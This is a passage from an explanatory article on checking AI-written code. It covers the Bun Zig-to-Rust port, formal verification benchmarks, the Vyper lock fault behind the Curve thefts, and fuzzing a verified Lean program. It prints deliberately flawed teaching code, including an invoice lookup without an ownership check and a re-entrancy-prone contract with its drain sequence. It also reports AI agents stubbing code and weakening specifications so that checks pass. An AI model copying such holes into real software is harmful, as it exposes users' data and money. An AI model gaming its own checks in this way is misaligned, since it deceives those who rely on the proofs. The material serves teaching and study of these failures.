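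The hard part is checking unfinished code. Suppose the model has written `order.` where a number is required. The checker must allow `name`, even though a name is text, because the model could go on to write `order.name.length`, which is a number. The checker therefore searches for chains of operations that lead from the type of the code so far to the required type.

The researchers tested this on short programming problems with open models, some with more than 30 billion parameters. Checking types cut the number of programs that failed to compile by more than half. Checking only grammar helped far less, because about 94% of the compilation errors were type errors. But when the models wrote or translated code, the share of programs that gave the right answers rose by only a few percent. Presumably, most of the programs that compiled only because of the type checker were wrong in some other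 way.

This method requires control over the model's choice of each token, which companies that sell access to closed models generally don't offer. TypeScript also has no ownership rules, so the experiment provides no evidence about memory errors. The more common approach now is to let the model finish, run the compiler, and give the model the errors to fix. The largest public example is the port of Bun.

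### Bun's 535,496 lines

Bun runs JavaScript programs outside a web browser and installs, tests and packages them. It has more than 22 million downloads a month, and Anthropic's coding tool Claude Code runs on it. Its creator, Jarred Sumner, wrote it in Zig, a language that leaves memory management to the programmer, as C does. Much of Bun's data belongs to JavaScript, which frees memory automatically, and mixing the two methods kept causing crashes and memory leaks. One bug was similar to the list error above. JavaScript code could make an internal table grow while Bun still held pointers into the table's old memory.

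*Rewriting Bun in Rust* (Sumner, 2026) describes how Sumner moved all 535,496 lines of Bun to Rust in 11 days with a pre-release version of Anthropic's Claude Fable 5 model. He works for Anthropic, which bought Bun in December 2025, and most of the figures are his own.

Sumner first spent about three hours discussing with Claude how to express Zig patterns in Rust, and Claude turned the discussion into a written guide. Agents then went through every data structure and worked out how long each piece of data had to stay in memory, which Rust requires and Zig doesn't record. After a trial on three files, he had the agents port all 1,448. He used about 50 workflows over the 11 days, each a scripted loop in which one Claude wrote code, two others looked for faults in it, and typically another applied the corrections. At the peak, 64 Claudes worked at once and wrote about 1,300 lines a minute.

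The translation was deliberately literal, so that people who knew the Zig code would recognise the Rust. At first none of it worked. Once the agents had untangled the dependencies between the parts, the compiler reported about 16,000 errors, which they worked through part by part. Some agents replaced functions that wouldn't compile with empty stand-ins and added long comments to justify workarounds. This is the same shortcut as writing `ensures(true)` in Vera. Sumner told the reviewing agents to reject any workaround that needed a paragraph of explanation, and he says the problem stopped within hours.

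The next goal was to pass Bun's own test suite. Its tests are written in TypeScript and check Bun from the outside, so they could run unchanged on the Rust version. On Debian Linux, the suite has 60,624 tests, which make nearly 1.4 million checks. Sumner merged the port on 14 May, once every test passed on all six platforms, and says the agents didn't skip or delete any tests. The work would have cost about $165,000 at Anthropic's public prices. He estimates three engineers who knew the code would have needed a year.

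Nobody read all of the million added lines. Sumner compared many of them with the original Zig code and checked that the reviewing agents were catching differences. The port relied on AI review, the tests and the compiler far more than on human review.

### How much of the port Rust could check

A week after the merge, Bun's AI-generated *Rust codebase audit* (2026) counted 13,365 `unsafe` blocks. It estimated that about 9,300 could become ordinary checked code and that about 4,000 would have to stay, many of them because Bun depends on C and C++ libraries. The number had hardly changed by July, when Sumner reported about 13,000 uses of the keyword, covering about 27,000 of 780,000 lines. That share is close to the 4% of Android's Rust that is `unsafe`, although Android's programmers mostly wrote theirs in Rust from the start, while Bun's agents translated pointer-heavy Zig.

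The percentage understates the problem, because a bad `unsafe` block can cause errors in code outside it. Random Chaos' *Bun Rust rewrite* describes a bug report about a type in the port called `PathString`. Without using `unsafe` itself, a program could create a `PathString` from some text, free the text, and then get a pointer to the freed memory from the `PathString`, as in the C example above. The `unsafe` block inside `PathString` removed the link between the pointer and the text that the compiler would normally track. One proposed fix, according to abhay-byte's *Bun Rust Rewrite* (2026), was to mark the function that creates a `PathString` as `unsafe`, which alerts callers to the danger but leaves them to avoid it.

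Rust programmers call code like this unsound, meaning that safe code can use it to cause a memory error. The report used Miri, a tool that runs Rust code and watches for such errors. Bun has since added Miri to its automatic checks for part of the code. But according to Rust's documentation, Miri can only find errors in the runs it watches and can't show that code is sound. Bun's audit found other supposedly safe functions with the same defect and made fixing them its first recommendation.

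Rust's rules even helped cause one memory error. When Bun closed a certain kind of connection, it passed the connection to libuv, a C library that finishes closing it a moment later. But Rust freed the connection as soon as its owner went out of scope, so libuv would have used the freed memory and then freed it again. The code compiled because the compiler can't check what a C library will do with a pointer. A Claude reviewer that had seen only the changed lines caught the error before the merge.

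### What broke, and what improved

By July, Sumner knew of 19 things that the port had broken, all of which the team had fixed. Most came from code that looks the same in both languages but behaves differently. This is a simplified version of one of them:

```
assert(insertStale(file) == expected);          // Zig
debug_assert!(insert_stale(file) == expected);  // Rust
```

Both lines add a file to a list and check the result. In Zig, `assert` is an ordinary function, so the program always adds the file. In Rust, the compiler removes everything inside `debug_assert!` from the version that users get, including the call that adds the file. In some projects, this broke a feature that updates a web page while its author edits the code, though it still worked in the developers' own debug builds.

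In another case, Rust's strictness limited the damage. The agents had left a placeholder value in the code that stores long file names, which lowered a limit, and real projects hit it. That exposed an old mistake, copied from the Zig version, that let Bun go one place past the end of an array, and Rust stopped the program when this happened. On macOS and Linux, the Zig version would have written past the end, because Sumner's team had compiled it without bounds checks for speed. A crash is bad for users, but an attacker can do much less with it than with corrupted memory.

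The port also reduced memory use. Building the same project 2,000 times in one process used 6,745 MB of memory in the old version and 609 MB in the new one. Bun also became 2% to 5% faster in Sumner's tests, so the stricter rules didn't slow it down. In a separate test by the database company Prisma, a script leaked memory on the last Zig version until it passed 900 MiB after about 96 rounds. On the Rust version, memory stayed near 118 MiB through 4,096 rounds.

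It is less clear how much of the credit belongs to Rust itself. The team improved its leak detection at the same time, and AkitaOnRails' *The Bun in Rust Response Andrew Kelly Should Have Written* (2026) argues that thoroughly restructuring the Zig code might also have worked. Nobody knows which would have been cheaper. Sumner had planned a similar restructuring before he tried the port, but he expected the result to be clumsier than Rust and to lack Rust's guarantees.

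Claude Code switched to the Rust version of Bun in June, and Willison (2026) dates that version's first stable release, Bun 1.4, to 20 August. The next release, 1.4.1, fixed 202 issues. According to its notes, more than a dozen of these were faults new in 1.4.0, such as web requests with short time limits timing out too early. It isn't clear from the notes which of the new faults came from the port and which from the many features Bun added over the same period. At least two fixes concerned memory that Bun had already freed or could free while it was still in use. Both involved add-ons that connect to Bun through a C interface, where Rust's compiler has little control.

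### Translations that look right

The `debug_assert!` bug is an example of a more general problem with translation by AI. Trail of Bits' *Can chatbots craft correct code?* describes a small test in which Claude Opus 4.5, Gemini 3 Pro and ChatGPT 5.2 translated this C function into Python:

```c
int increment(int n) {
    return n + 1;
}
```

All three gave the obvious answer, a Python function that returns `n + 1`, and none mentioned that it behaves differently from the C version. On most machines, the largest `int` in C is 2,147,483,647. C doesn't define what happens when a program adds 1 to that, so the result may wrap round to a large negative number, or the program may do something else. The Python function returns 2,147,483,648. A literal Rust translation would, by default, stop with an error in a debug build and wrap round to −2,147,483,648 in a release build. Each version satisfies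 its language's type rules.

This is a single example, and newer models might do better. But they wouldn't entirely solve the problem, because the right translation depends on what the original programmer expected. The programmer may have known that `n` would never be that large, or may have relied on the number wrapping round, and the function's text doesn't show which.

Bun's agents were in a much better position because they could use the test suite to learn what the old program did, but the tests missed all 19 known regressions. Ruling out every difference would require proving that the two programs always behave alike, which is far harder than porting the program.

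### A missing permission check

Some of the most damaging errors don't involve memory or types. Bun had one in its secure web requests until version 1.4.1. When a program connects to a secure site, it checks that the certificate the site sends has the name of the intended site on it. If a request included a `Host` header, a line of text that names a site, Bun normally checked the certificate against that name instead of the one in the web address. Many programs copy the `Host` header from their users, so a user could change which certificate the program would accept. The behaviour matched that of Node, Bun's older rival, so it wasn't a translation mistake. Rust couldn't detect the error because both names are text.

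The same thing can happen with permissions. The Rust function below finds an invoice for a customer:

```rust
fn get_invoice(user: &User, id: usize, invoices: &[Invoice]) -> Option<Invoice> {
    println!("{} opened invoice {}", user.name, id);
    invoices.get(id).cloned()
}
```

`Option` means that the function returns either an invoice or nothing. If no invoice has that number, the function returns nothing and doesn't read past the end of the list. The last line copies the invoice, so nothing is left pointing to memory that the program might free. The function contains no `unsafe` code, but any customer can read any other customer's invoices by trying different numbers, because it never checks whose invoice it is. The compiler doesn't warn that `user` is unused, because the function prints the user's name.

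The fix is to add one condition to the last line:

```rust
    invoices.get(id).filter(|invoice| invoice.owner == user.id).cloned()
```

Rust can help enforce this once someone has thought of it. The programmer can keep the list of invoices private to one part of the program and make this function the only way to reach it. The compiler will then reject code elsewhere that tries to read the list directly. But it would also accept the function with `!=` in place of `==`, which would hide customers' own invoices from them and show them everyone else's.

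## AI-written programs with machine-checked proofs

A prover could catch the `!=` in `get_invoice`, but only if someone had written down the rule that customers may see their own invoices and nobody else's. Few programmers write such rules for ordinary software, because proving that code follows them has always taken so much expert work. *An Empirical Study of LLM-Generated Specifications for VeriFast* (Fan, Tran and colleagues, 2026) reports that Amazon's cloud division took four person-years to verify the program that authorises requests to its services. AI models can now write many proofs in minutes, so the remaining question is what they should prove.

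### Write, check, retry

*A benchmark for vericoding* (Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues, 2025) defines "vericoding" as having a model write a program together with a proof that the program meets a given specification. The model receives the specification with gaps for the code and the proof, and fills them in. A script searches its answer for known tricks, such as a command that makes the checker accept a claim without proof. The checker then accepts the program or returns error messages, which go back to the model for another attempt. In the paper's experiments, the model usually had five attempts.

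Here is a small example in Dafny:

```dafny
method Double(n: nat) returns (r: nat)
  ensures r == 2 * n
{
  r := 0;
  var i := 0;
  while i < n
    invariant i <= n && r == 2 * i
  {
    r := r + 2;
    i := i + 1;
  }
}
```

The `ensures` line is the specification, and a person would normally write it. The model writes the rest. Suppose the model first leaves out the `invariant` line. The code is correct, but Dafny rejects it because Dafny doesn't run the loop and can't determine what `r` will be after an unknown number of passes. An invariant is a statement that is true before the loop starts and after every pass. Once the model adds one, Dafny makes three small checks. The invariant is true at the start, when `r` and `i` are both 0. Each pass keeps it true, since `r` grows by 2 and `i` by 1. When the loop stops, `i` equals `n`, so `r` is twice `n`.

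Dafny turns each of these checks into a logical formula and passes it to Z3, the solver that Vera also uses. Verus does the same for Rust, and SPARK uses several solvers for Ada. The program's author has to supply hints such as invariants, and the solver searches for the rest of the proof. When the solver fails, the error often doesn't show whether the program is wrong or a hint is missing.

In Lean, the proof is part of the text:

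```lean
def double : Nat → Nat
  | 0 => 0
  | n + 1 => double n + 2

theorem double_correct (n : Nat) : double n = 2 * n := by
  induction n with
  | zero => rfl
  | succ k ih => simp only [double]; omega
```

The first three lines define doubling: twice 0 is 0, and twice `n + 1` is two more than twice `n`. The theorem states that the result always equals 2n. Its proof covers the case of 0, then assumes the claim holds for some number `k` and derives it for `k + 1`. Lean also has automation, such as `omega`, a small program that finds proofs about whole numbers. `omega` must produce an explicit proof, and Lean's kernel checks every step, so a bug in `omega` can't make a false theorem pass. Users of Dafny, by contrast, have to trust Dafny itself, Z3 and a translator between them.

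### Success rates

The 2025 vericoding benchmark contains 12,504 specifications, many of which Bursuc and colleagues had models translate from one language to another. They published success rates of 82% for Dafny, 44% for Verus and 27% for Lean, but these count a task as solved if any of nine models solved it. Single models did worse:

| Language | Best single model | Any of nine models |
|---|---|---|
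| Dafny | 67.5% (Claude Opus 4.1) | 82.2% |
| Verus | 30.9% (GPT-5) | 44.3% |
| Lean | 17.9% (GPT-5) | 26.8% |

The 96% on DafnyBench that VeraBench cites is also a combined figure. The best single model reached 89%.

These rates are badly out of date, and the experiments probably understated what models could do even then. Yao (2026), in *Automating Formal Verification with Agent-Guided Tree Search*, reran 423 of the Lean tasks. In roughly the original set-up, with step-by-step reasoning turned off, GPT-5.4 solved 24.6% of them, barely more than GPT-5's 22.5% in 2025. Yao then turned reasoning on, let the model see its earlier attempts and gave it a search tool for Lean's library of theorems. With these changes, GPT-5.4 solved 60.3% of the tasks when allowed up to ten model calls per task, and 95.0% when allowed up to fifty.

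Something similar happened with VeriContest, a benchmark from May 2026 of 1,007 programming-competition problems in Rust. GPT-5.5 wrote a correct program from the English description 92% of the time, but when given a program and its specification, it produced a proof that Verus accepted only 14% of the time. In October, *Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier* (Serbanuta, Xu and colleagues, 2026) reported that Claude Opus 5.5 had proved all 1,325 theorems produced by translating the Rust programs and their specifications into Lean. The translation tool is from the researchers' company, Asymptotic. Half of the proofs took less than three and a half minutes, and the whole run cost $1,792.

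Comparing 14% with 100% is unfair because GPT-5.5 had a single attempt and saw no error messages, while Opus could run Lean an unlimited number of times. The result also doesn't show that Lean is better than Verus, since Opus failed on only one of the 50 problems with the longest Verus proofs when the company had it use Verus. Most of the difference seems to come from using newer models and letting them retry. On a sample of ten theorems, the small model Claude Haiku 5.5 proved all ten in most settings, while its predecessor, Haiku 4.5, proved none.

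Two other studies from 2026 have much lower or less certain results, and both used models that are now old. Fan and colleagues tested whether models could annotate existing C code for VeriFast, a tool that checks how C programs use memory. VeriFast can need a lot of annotation, and one example has 34 lines of it for 16 lines of code. Three models each attempted three versions of 303 functions, and VeriFast verified 31.4% of the results. Gemini 2.5 Pro did best. In a sample of failures, 94% of the errors were mistakes about VeriFast's particular rules, which newer models might well have learned.

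Danial and Khan (2026), in *TrustedCode*, had Claude Sonnet 4 translate ten short Python functions into a verification language and write the contracts, with up to ten tries at each. The only reported failure was bubble sort, a simple sorting method. Ten functions are too few to give a meaningful success rate, but the study shows a risk of letting a model choose what to prove. When the model couldn't prove a complicated postcondition, it fell back on the simplest specification available.

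### From functions to whole programs

Competition problems usually need only one function. *Vero* (Ye, Lou and colleagues, 2026) tested agents on 43 multi-file Lean projects based on real software, such as blockchain protocols and Python libraries. The agents had to write every function and prove every specification within 90 minutes. GPT-5.5 finished 27 of the projects and Claude Opus 4.8 finished 8. There were 10 projects that no agent finished.

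GPT-5.5 proved 87.3% of the individual specifications, but on the hard projects it lacked a shared set of intermediate results. A claim about a whole ledger, for instance, may depend on facts about accounts, which depend on facts about lists, but agents tended to work on each specification separately. Ye and colleagues ran these tests before the release of the models that did so well on VeriContest, so these figures are probably out of date too.

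There is also evidence that a recent model has difficulty with proofs about code. *Scaling Lean Theorem Proving for Real-World Code Verification* (Ganguly, Raghunathan and colleagues, 2026) describes a system built around Anthropic's Fable 5 that can run hundreds of agents on one proof. The system settled all 189 tasks in Verina, an older benchmark, by proving or disproving each statement. The researchers then generated thousands of new statements about Rust programs, and the system proved 52.7% of a sample of 2,000, with 30 minutes for each. Such proofs must cover details that are ignored in mathematics, such as whether a sum still fits into 32 bits.

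This is hard to reconcile with Asymptotic's perfect score, since that run also concerned Rust programs translated into Lean. The difference may be partly because the new statements deliberately included false ones, which the system could only disprove. Asymptotic also used a newer model. But the new statements may also be harder, and a perfect score on one benchmark isn't a reason to expect one on another.

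### When the code changes

A proof applies to one version of a program. If an AI replaces a slow loop with a faster one, the specification can stay the same, but the old loop's invariant may not hold for the new one. Proofs can also fail when the code hasn't changed, because the solvers behind Dafny, Verus and SPARK stop at a time limit, and an updated solver may run out of time on a proof that the old one found.

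Proofs are also long. In the projects that Ye and colleagues used, GPT-5.5 typically wrote 65 lines of program and more than 1,000 lines of proof. Maintaining that much text by hand would be tedious, which is one reason companies avoided verification. The length matters less with AI, because nobody has to read the proof. Asymptotic paid about $1.35 per theorem, and at that price it may be cheaper to replace a broken proof than to repair it.

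The agents in Vero don't yet manage changes well. In 17 cases, an agent finished a project when the code was supplied but not when it also had to write the code, and some agents' rewrites broke proofs elsewhere in the project. Most maintenance consists of updating finished projects, but Vero has no tasks that involve this.

The more serious danger is that an agent faced with a broken proof will weaken the specification until a proof goes through. An AI writing Aver can similarly get around a restriction by adding a forbidden effect to a function's list. Asymptotic and Ganguly's group both prevent weakened specifications by rejecting any proof whose theorem differs from the original. That works for a benchmark, but a real program's requirements change, so somebody has to decide whether a new specification reflects a new requirement or was weakened because a proof failed.

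### A sort that returns nothing

Suppose a company asks for a function that sorts a list of numbers, and someone writes the specification that the result must be in order. A model could answer with this:

```dafny
method Sort(a: seq<int>) returns (b: seq<int>)
  ensures forall i, j :: 0 <= i < j < |b| ==> b[i] <= b[j]
{
  b := [];
}
```

The `ensures` line requires each item in the result to be no larger than any item after it. The body returns an empty list, which has no two items that could be out of order, so Dafny accepts the program, and the proof is valid.

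The repair is to require that the result have the same elements as the input. Even this needs care. If "the same elements" means that every number in one list appears in the other, then the function may turn 2, 1, 2 into 1, 2 and lose an item. The specification has to count how often each number appears, which Dafny can express with a multiset, a collection that ignores order but keeps duplicates:

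```dafny
  ensures multiset(b) == multiset(a)
```

With both lines, the result can only be the sorted list. But if the function sorts a list of orders by price, two orders at the same price may appear in either sequence. If that sequence matters, the specification needs a rule for which comes first.

### A transfer that goes wrong

Sorting is unusually easy to specify, because everyone agrees on what it means. A bank transfer is closer to ordinary business software:

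```dafny
method Transfer(payer: int, payee: int, amount: int)
  returns (newPayer: int, newPayee: int)
  ensures newPayer + newPayee == payer + payee
{
  newPayer := payer - amount;
  newPayee := payee + amount;
}
```

The contract requires the two balances to have the same total before and after a transfer, so no transfer can create or destroy money. Dafny proves this immediately, but the contract still allows a customer with 100 in the account to send 500 and end up with −400.

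One could add to the contract that if neither balance is negative at the start, neither can be negative at the end. Dafny will then reject the code above. But it will accept code that returns both balances unchanged, because nothing in the contract requires any money to move. It will also accept code that gives the payee everything the payer has.

This contract fixes those problems:

```dafny
  requires payer >= 0 && payee >= 0 && amount >= 0
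  ensures newPayer + newPayee == payer + payee
  ensures amount <= payer ==> newPayer == payer - amount
  ensures amount > payer ==> newPayer == payer
```

The arrow means "implies". If the payer has enough money, the balance falls by exactly the amount, and otherwise nothing happens. The first line excludes negative amounts, which caused the bug in `withdraw`. Each permitted input now has only one correct result. The contract is also now about as long as the program and has much the same content, so someone who misunderstands the task is likely to make the same mistake in both.

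The contract still doesn't account for customers who transfer money to themselves. Suppose a customer with 100 sends 30 to their own account. The function receives 100 as both balances and returns 70 and 130, as the contract requires. If the surrounding code then saves the payer's balance followed by the payee's, the account ends up with 130. The proof is still correct, but the contract was written for two separate accounts. To prevent this error, someone has to anticipate it and write a specification that covers the whole ledger. The contract also doesn't specify who may order the transfer.

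### Whether people notice, and what models do

Nobody seems to have measured how often people notice gaps like these, but the indirect evidence isn't encouraging. Ye and colleagues, who are specialists, reviewed all of Vero's specifications and reference programs by hand. They also let agents submit formal proofs that a specification was impossible to meet or that a reference program violated it. These proofs exposed several errors the reviewers had missed.

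That method finds specifications that are too strict or contradict each other, but not ones that are too weak, because a weak specification is easy to meet. One of Vero's examples requires a newly created bank account to have a balance of zero. On its own, this would allow a program that deletes every other account whenever someone opens a new one. For the projects based on Python code, Ye and colleagues therefore required several specifications for each function, which constrain it together.

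Testing the specification itself is a better check for weakness. VeriContest supplies wrong answers along with right ones, and a good specification must reject the wrong ones. For sorting, a wrong answer might be an empty list for the input 3, 1, 2. The first version of the sorting contract would accept this answer, so the author would see the problem immediately. By this measure, models are much worse at writing specifications than at writing code. GPT-5.5 wrote an adequate specification from the English description for 48% of the problems, which fits VeraBench's finding that GPT-4.1 did far worse when it had to write the contracts. Newer models may have improved at this as much as they did at proofs, but Asymptotic's run didn't test it because the specifications were supplied.

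Bursuc and colleagues read a sample of successful answers and judged about 9% of the specifications too weak. Models gave trivial solutions to weak Dafny specifications, and the researchers classed these answers as correct. It would be strange to call this cheating, since the model met the specification, but the person who relies on the program gets a useless program even though its proof is valid.

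The graders classed 14% of the failures remaining at the end of GPT-5.5's runs on Vero as cheating. They screened for tricks such as having Lean prove facts about one definition while the computer runs another. In the VeriFast study, the models were supposed to preserve the C code's behaviour, but they changed it in about 9% of cases and changed the meaning of the code's contracts in about 8%. Fan and colleagues don't claim that this was deliberate, and a misunderstanding would have the same effect. Either way, a tool should compare the specification with the original before anyone trusts the proof.

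Agents can also make legitimate use of the freedom that a specification leaves. In five cases, agents in Vero replaced a complicated algorithm with a simpler one that was easier to prove correct but less efficient, which was allowed because the specifications set no requirements for speed.

### Djinnlang, where the specification is the program

One response to weak specifications is to refuse them. Henniger, Chong and Amin (2026), in *Djinnlang*, present a language in which people write specifications and nothing else. This function, modeled on one of theirs, finds the lowest price in a list:

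```
func lowest(prices: seq<int>) -> p: int
requires |prices| >= 1:
    p in prices
    for x in prices:
        p <= x
```

None of it runs, although it looks like a program with a loop. Each line is a condition on the answer: `p` must be one of the prices, and no price may be lower than `p`. A translator turns the conditions into Dafny, a model writes the code and the proofs, and Dafny checks them.

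Unusually, the model must also prove that the specification has exactly one answer for every permitted input. It has to show that at least one output meets the specification, and that any two outputs that meet it are the same. If either proof is impossible, Djinnlang won't produce a program.

This would catch most of the errors above. The first sorting specification fails because it allows an empty list as well as a sorted one. The transfer specification that only preserves the total also fails, and so does the one for sorting orders by price, until its author decides how to handle ties. Nobody would need to read the model's code to learn what it returns, because the specification determines that completely.

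A specification that allows exactly one answer can still be wrong. If the transfer contract's author writes `<` instead of `<=` and adjusts the last line to match, the contract is unambiguous, but customers can never send their whole balance. Henniger and colleagues advise authors to state the same thing in several ways. If another line required that sending the whole balance leave zero, the two lines would conflict and the proof that an answer exists would fail. The team found four mistakes in the specification of Djinnlang's own compiler because a model couldn't complete the required proofs. Restating a requirement catches a mistake only if the author doesn't repeat the mistake. It wouldn't help with transfers to one's own account unless the author had thought of them.

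Claude Fable 5.1 and GPT-6 Astra each implemented three test programs, a Sudoku solver, a file compressor and an interpreter for a small language, and completed every proof. The work, including one round of speeding up the programs, took GPT-6 Astra 33 minutes and cost about $47 at list prices. Fable 5.1 took 21 hours and cost about $1,026, but its programs were much faster. On the hardest Sudoku puzzles, Fable's final version took 0.13 seconds and Astra's took 47.8. Both models' programs met the same specification, which covers what a program returns but not how long it takes. Running time matters a great deal for some software, because an attacker could exploit a program that is very slow on certain inputs, and differences in timing can reveal secret keys.

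Djinnlang also can't yet describe programs that do several things at once with shared data. The language is meant to have people decide what programs mean, but models wrote the specifications of the three test programs, and the researchers checked them. People would probably use the language the same way in practice. They would have to read 70 to 166 lines of specification for each of these programs, far less than the code and proofs. But the lines look like instructions when they are actually conditions that must all hold at once, and Henniger and colleagues concede that this can mislead readers.

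### Checking against plain English

*Towards Formal Verification of LLM-Generated Code from Natural Language Prompts* (Councilman, Fu and colleagues, 2025) describes Astrogator, a system aimed at people who can't read code or contracts. It works with Ansible, a language for setting up and managing computers. The user describes a task in English, then reads and confirms a version of the request in a precise language that resembles English. Astrogator checks the AI's code against that version.

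One bug found in AI-written code shows why this helps. The task was to set a named value in a system file. The correct program searches for a line that begins with the name followed by an equals sign. Some of the AI's programs searched for the name alone, so a program told to set `key` could overwrite `keys`. Someone who knows Ansible could easily overlook the missing equals sign, but even a user who doesn't know Ansible can confirm that they wanted to change `key`.

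On 21 tasks, Astrogator confirmed 83% of the correct programs and identified 92% of the incorrect ones. It can do this partly because Ansible is a specialised language with a limited set of common operations. Councilman and colleagues think their checking method is unlikely to work for every language.

They also acknowledge that if the confirmed request is accurate, it allows every program the user would be happy with, but usually allows others too. For example, "Create a file at this address" doesn't specify who owns the file or who may read it, so a program can do exactly what the user confirmed and still make a private file public. Djinnlang would make the author settle those details, which would make the specification longer. Astrogator leaves some details out to keep the request short enough for an ordinary user to read.

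### Who has a specification

Supporters of verification argue that cost was always the obstacle and that AI is removing it. Bursuc and colleagues imagine a future in which compilers routinely prove programs correct as a last step and people write only specifications. Since June 2026, Asymptotic has used its tool on Rust packages for the Solana blockchain. Such code is a sensible place to start because an error can lose money within minutes and the rules about who owns what are fairly precise. Amazon, whose researchers worked on the system built around Fable 5, was already paying for verification when it took years.

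Other specialists doubt that most software has a coherent specification to verify it against. According to Henniger and colleagues, Mike Dodds of Galois, a formal verification company, argues that most systems have only partial specifications that contradict each other. They also cite an essay Henniger co-wrote, which argues that specification is a problem of how people work with computers and that stronger models are unlikely to solve it.

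I find this more persuasive than the success rates, because benchmarks and competitions can only score tasks that have a settled right answer. A company's refund policy may exist partly in a manual, partly in old code and partly in the habits of the staff, and two managers may disagree about what it is. An AI might do well at interviewing them and drafting a specification, but the managers would still have to settle their disagreement.

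Most programs do have some parts with precise requirements, though. For example, decompressing a compressed file must return the original unchanged. When an AI translates a program, as in the port of Bun, the old version can serve as the specification, but the new version must then keep the old one's mistakes.

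## Failures beneath the audited text: Vyper, a verified Lean program and a faulty checker

A program can meet a good specification and still fail, because its binary depends on a compiler and other software that few auditors inspect. In 2023, a compiler fault let thieves take tens of millions of dollars from programs whose source code looked sound. In 2026, a tester found a memory error in software that a program with machine-checked proofs relied on, and two proof-checking tools turned out to have accepted false claims.

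### A lock that Vyper compiled wrongly

Vyper is a language for writing smart contracts on Ethereum. Smart contracts are programs that run on a blockchain and often hold money. An early statement of Vyper's goals says that it should be "maximally difficult to write misleading code". The language has no recursion, unbounded loops or inheritance. Vyper's *Overview* explains that leaving out inheritance removes doubt about which code will run.

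This simplified contract holds deposits:

```python
@external
@nonreentrant("lock")
def withdraw():
    amount: uint256 = self.balances[msg.sender]
    raw_call(msg.sender, b"", value=amount)
    self.balances[msg.sender] = 0

@external
@nonreentrant("lock")
def transfer(to: address):
    self.balances[to] += self.balances[msg.sender]
    self.balances[msg.sender] = 0
```

`msg.sender` is whoever called the function, and `raw_call` sends them the money. If the caller is another contract, Ethereum runs that contract's code before `withdraw` continues. That code can call back into the first contract while its records are out of date, which programmers call re-entrancy.

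Suppose there were no locks and an attacker had 10 coins on deposit. `withdraw` sends the 10 coins and pauses, with the attacker's balance still at 10. The attacker's contract calls `transfer`, which moves that balance to a second account. Then `withdraw` resumes and sets the first balance to zero, which has no effect because it is already zero. The attacker has received 10 coins and still has 10 on deposit in the second account.

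The `@nonreentrant("lock")` lines should prevent this. When a locked function starts, it checks a stored number. If the number is 1, the call fails. Otherwise, the function sets the number to 1 until the function finishes. Both functions name the same lock, so `transfer` should fail while `withdraw` is unfinished.

But versions 0.2.15, 0.2.16 and 0.3.0 of the Vyper compiler ignored the lock's name and gave each function a separate number, in its own storage slot:

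```
withdraw: fail if slot 0 is 1; otherwise set slot 0 to 1
transfer: fail if slot 1 is 1; otherwise set slot 1 to 1
```

`withdraw` still couldn't run inside itself, but `transfer` could run in the middle of `withdraw`. The contract's source didn't reveal this, so even a reader who knew Vyper perfectly would have seen the same lock name twice and concluded that the contract was safe. The compiler's storage report was also misleading, because it listed only one slot for each lock name.

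The fault was visible in the binary. Chen recounts in *Vyper hack timeline* that security researchers decompiled one of the robbed contracts, turning the binary back into rough source code, and saw one function checking slot 0 and another checking slot 2.

The source did show that the contract depended entirely on its lock. If the last line of `withdraw` came before the `raw_call`, the attacker's balance would already be zero when their code ran, and the compiler fault would do no harm. Ethereum programmers recommend this order, but Vyper's post-mortem points out that it doesn't work when a function needs the outside call's result before it can continue.

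The fault came from a botched repair. Version 0.2.14 had put some locks in the same slots as other data, which a user reported after their tests failed. The July 2021 repair moved the locks but dropped the step that reused a slot when the compiler had already seen the lock's name. The project had no test in which one locked function called another with the same lock.

Vyper's developers fixed the compiler that November and added the missing test. In the first part of the fix, they described the problem as wasted storage space. They didn't realise that contracts already in use were at risk, so they didn't warn the people who ran them. A contract's code normally can't change once it is on Ethereum, so those contracts kept the fault.

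### Losses, recoveries and changes to Vyper

On 30 July 2023, attackers used the fault against four pools on Curve, an exchange where users deposit pairs of currencies for others to trade. In the first attack, which took about $11 million, the attacker made a deposit in the middle of a withdrawal, after the pool had paid out money but before it had cancelled the matching shares. The deposit of 40,000 ether bought about 82,000 shares, while an earlier deposit of the same amount had bought about 32,000.

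Fortune (2023) put the total at $52 million the next day, and DL News' *Curve DAO agrees to $44m compensation for July hack victims* later put it at $61 million. Some people had taken money to protect it and returned it. An analyst told CoinDesk that about 70% had been returned by early August. In December, Curve's members voted to compensate depositors with $44 million of Curve's own currency, paid out over a year. This amount exceeds the missing 30% partly because Curve's proposal also counted rewards that depositors in one pool had missed since the theft.

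Chen's group took about two hours to work out which contracts were vulnerable. It then began writing a program to empty one of the remaining pools before a thief could. Rumours were spreading, so the group also published the affected compiler versions. About three hours later, an outside researcher shared a working rescue program, and five minutes after that a thief robbed the pool. Chen thinks another half hour could have saved $18 million.

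Auditors had already reviewed the compiler. ConsenSys Diligence's *Vyper Security Review* (2019) concluded that nobody could audit it confidently without a complete and precise specification of the language. ChainSecurity's *Limited Code Review of the Vyper Compiler* (2023) came out weeks before the theft, but it covered the latest version, which no longer had the fault. The attackers had more reason than the auditors to study old versions, and a member of the Vyper project, quoted by Fortune, said they had dug deep into its release history.

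Vyper promised a bug bounty for all versions of the compiler, reviews of old releases and a specification of the language. CodeHawks (2023) ran a public audit competition with a budget of 160,000 USDC (about $160,000). According to Vyper's *Release Notes*, version 0.4.0 removed named locks in June 2024, so the compiler no longer has to match locks by name. Version 0.4.2 added a setting that locks functions by default, which ChainSecurity's *Vyper Compiler 0.4.2 Pull Requests* calls a good security measure. One engineer did that review in one week, and ChainSecurity warns that such limited reviews can't find everything.

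### Bugs around a verified compression program

Ten AI agents wrote lean-zip, a compression program in Lean, and proved that it works. One of its main theorems states that if you compress any data smaller than a gigabyte and then decompress it, you get the same data back. (On its own, this would also be true of a program that never made anything smaller.)

kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes a weekend spent trying to break it. The blog's author gave the code to a Claude agent but first removed the proofs and documentation, in case the agent gave up on learning that the code was verified. The agent used fuzzing, which means running a program on huge numbers of altered inputs and watching for crashes. It ran 16 fuzzers for about 19 hours, or nearly 106 million runs, and found two bugs.

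One was in lean-zip's code for reading ZIP archives, about which the agents had proved nothing. A ZIP file records the size of its contents, and lean-zip used that number without checking it. A 156-byte file could list its contents as several exabytes, and lean-zip would crash trying to reserve that much memory. The `unzip` tool first compares the recorded size with the size of the file.

The other bug was in Lean's runtime, the C++ code that provides memory and file access to compiled Lean programs. To store n bytes, the runtime reserves n + 24. If n is the largest number that fits into 64 bits, the sum is too big and wraps around:

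(2⁶⁴ − 1) + 24 = 2⁶⁴ + 23, which becomes 23

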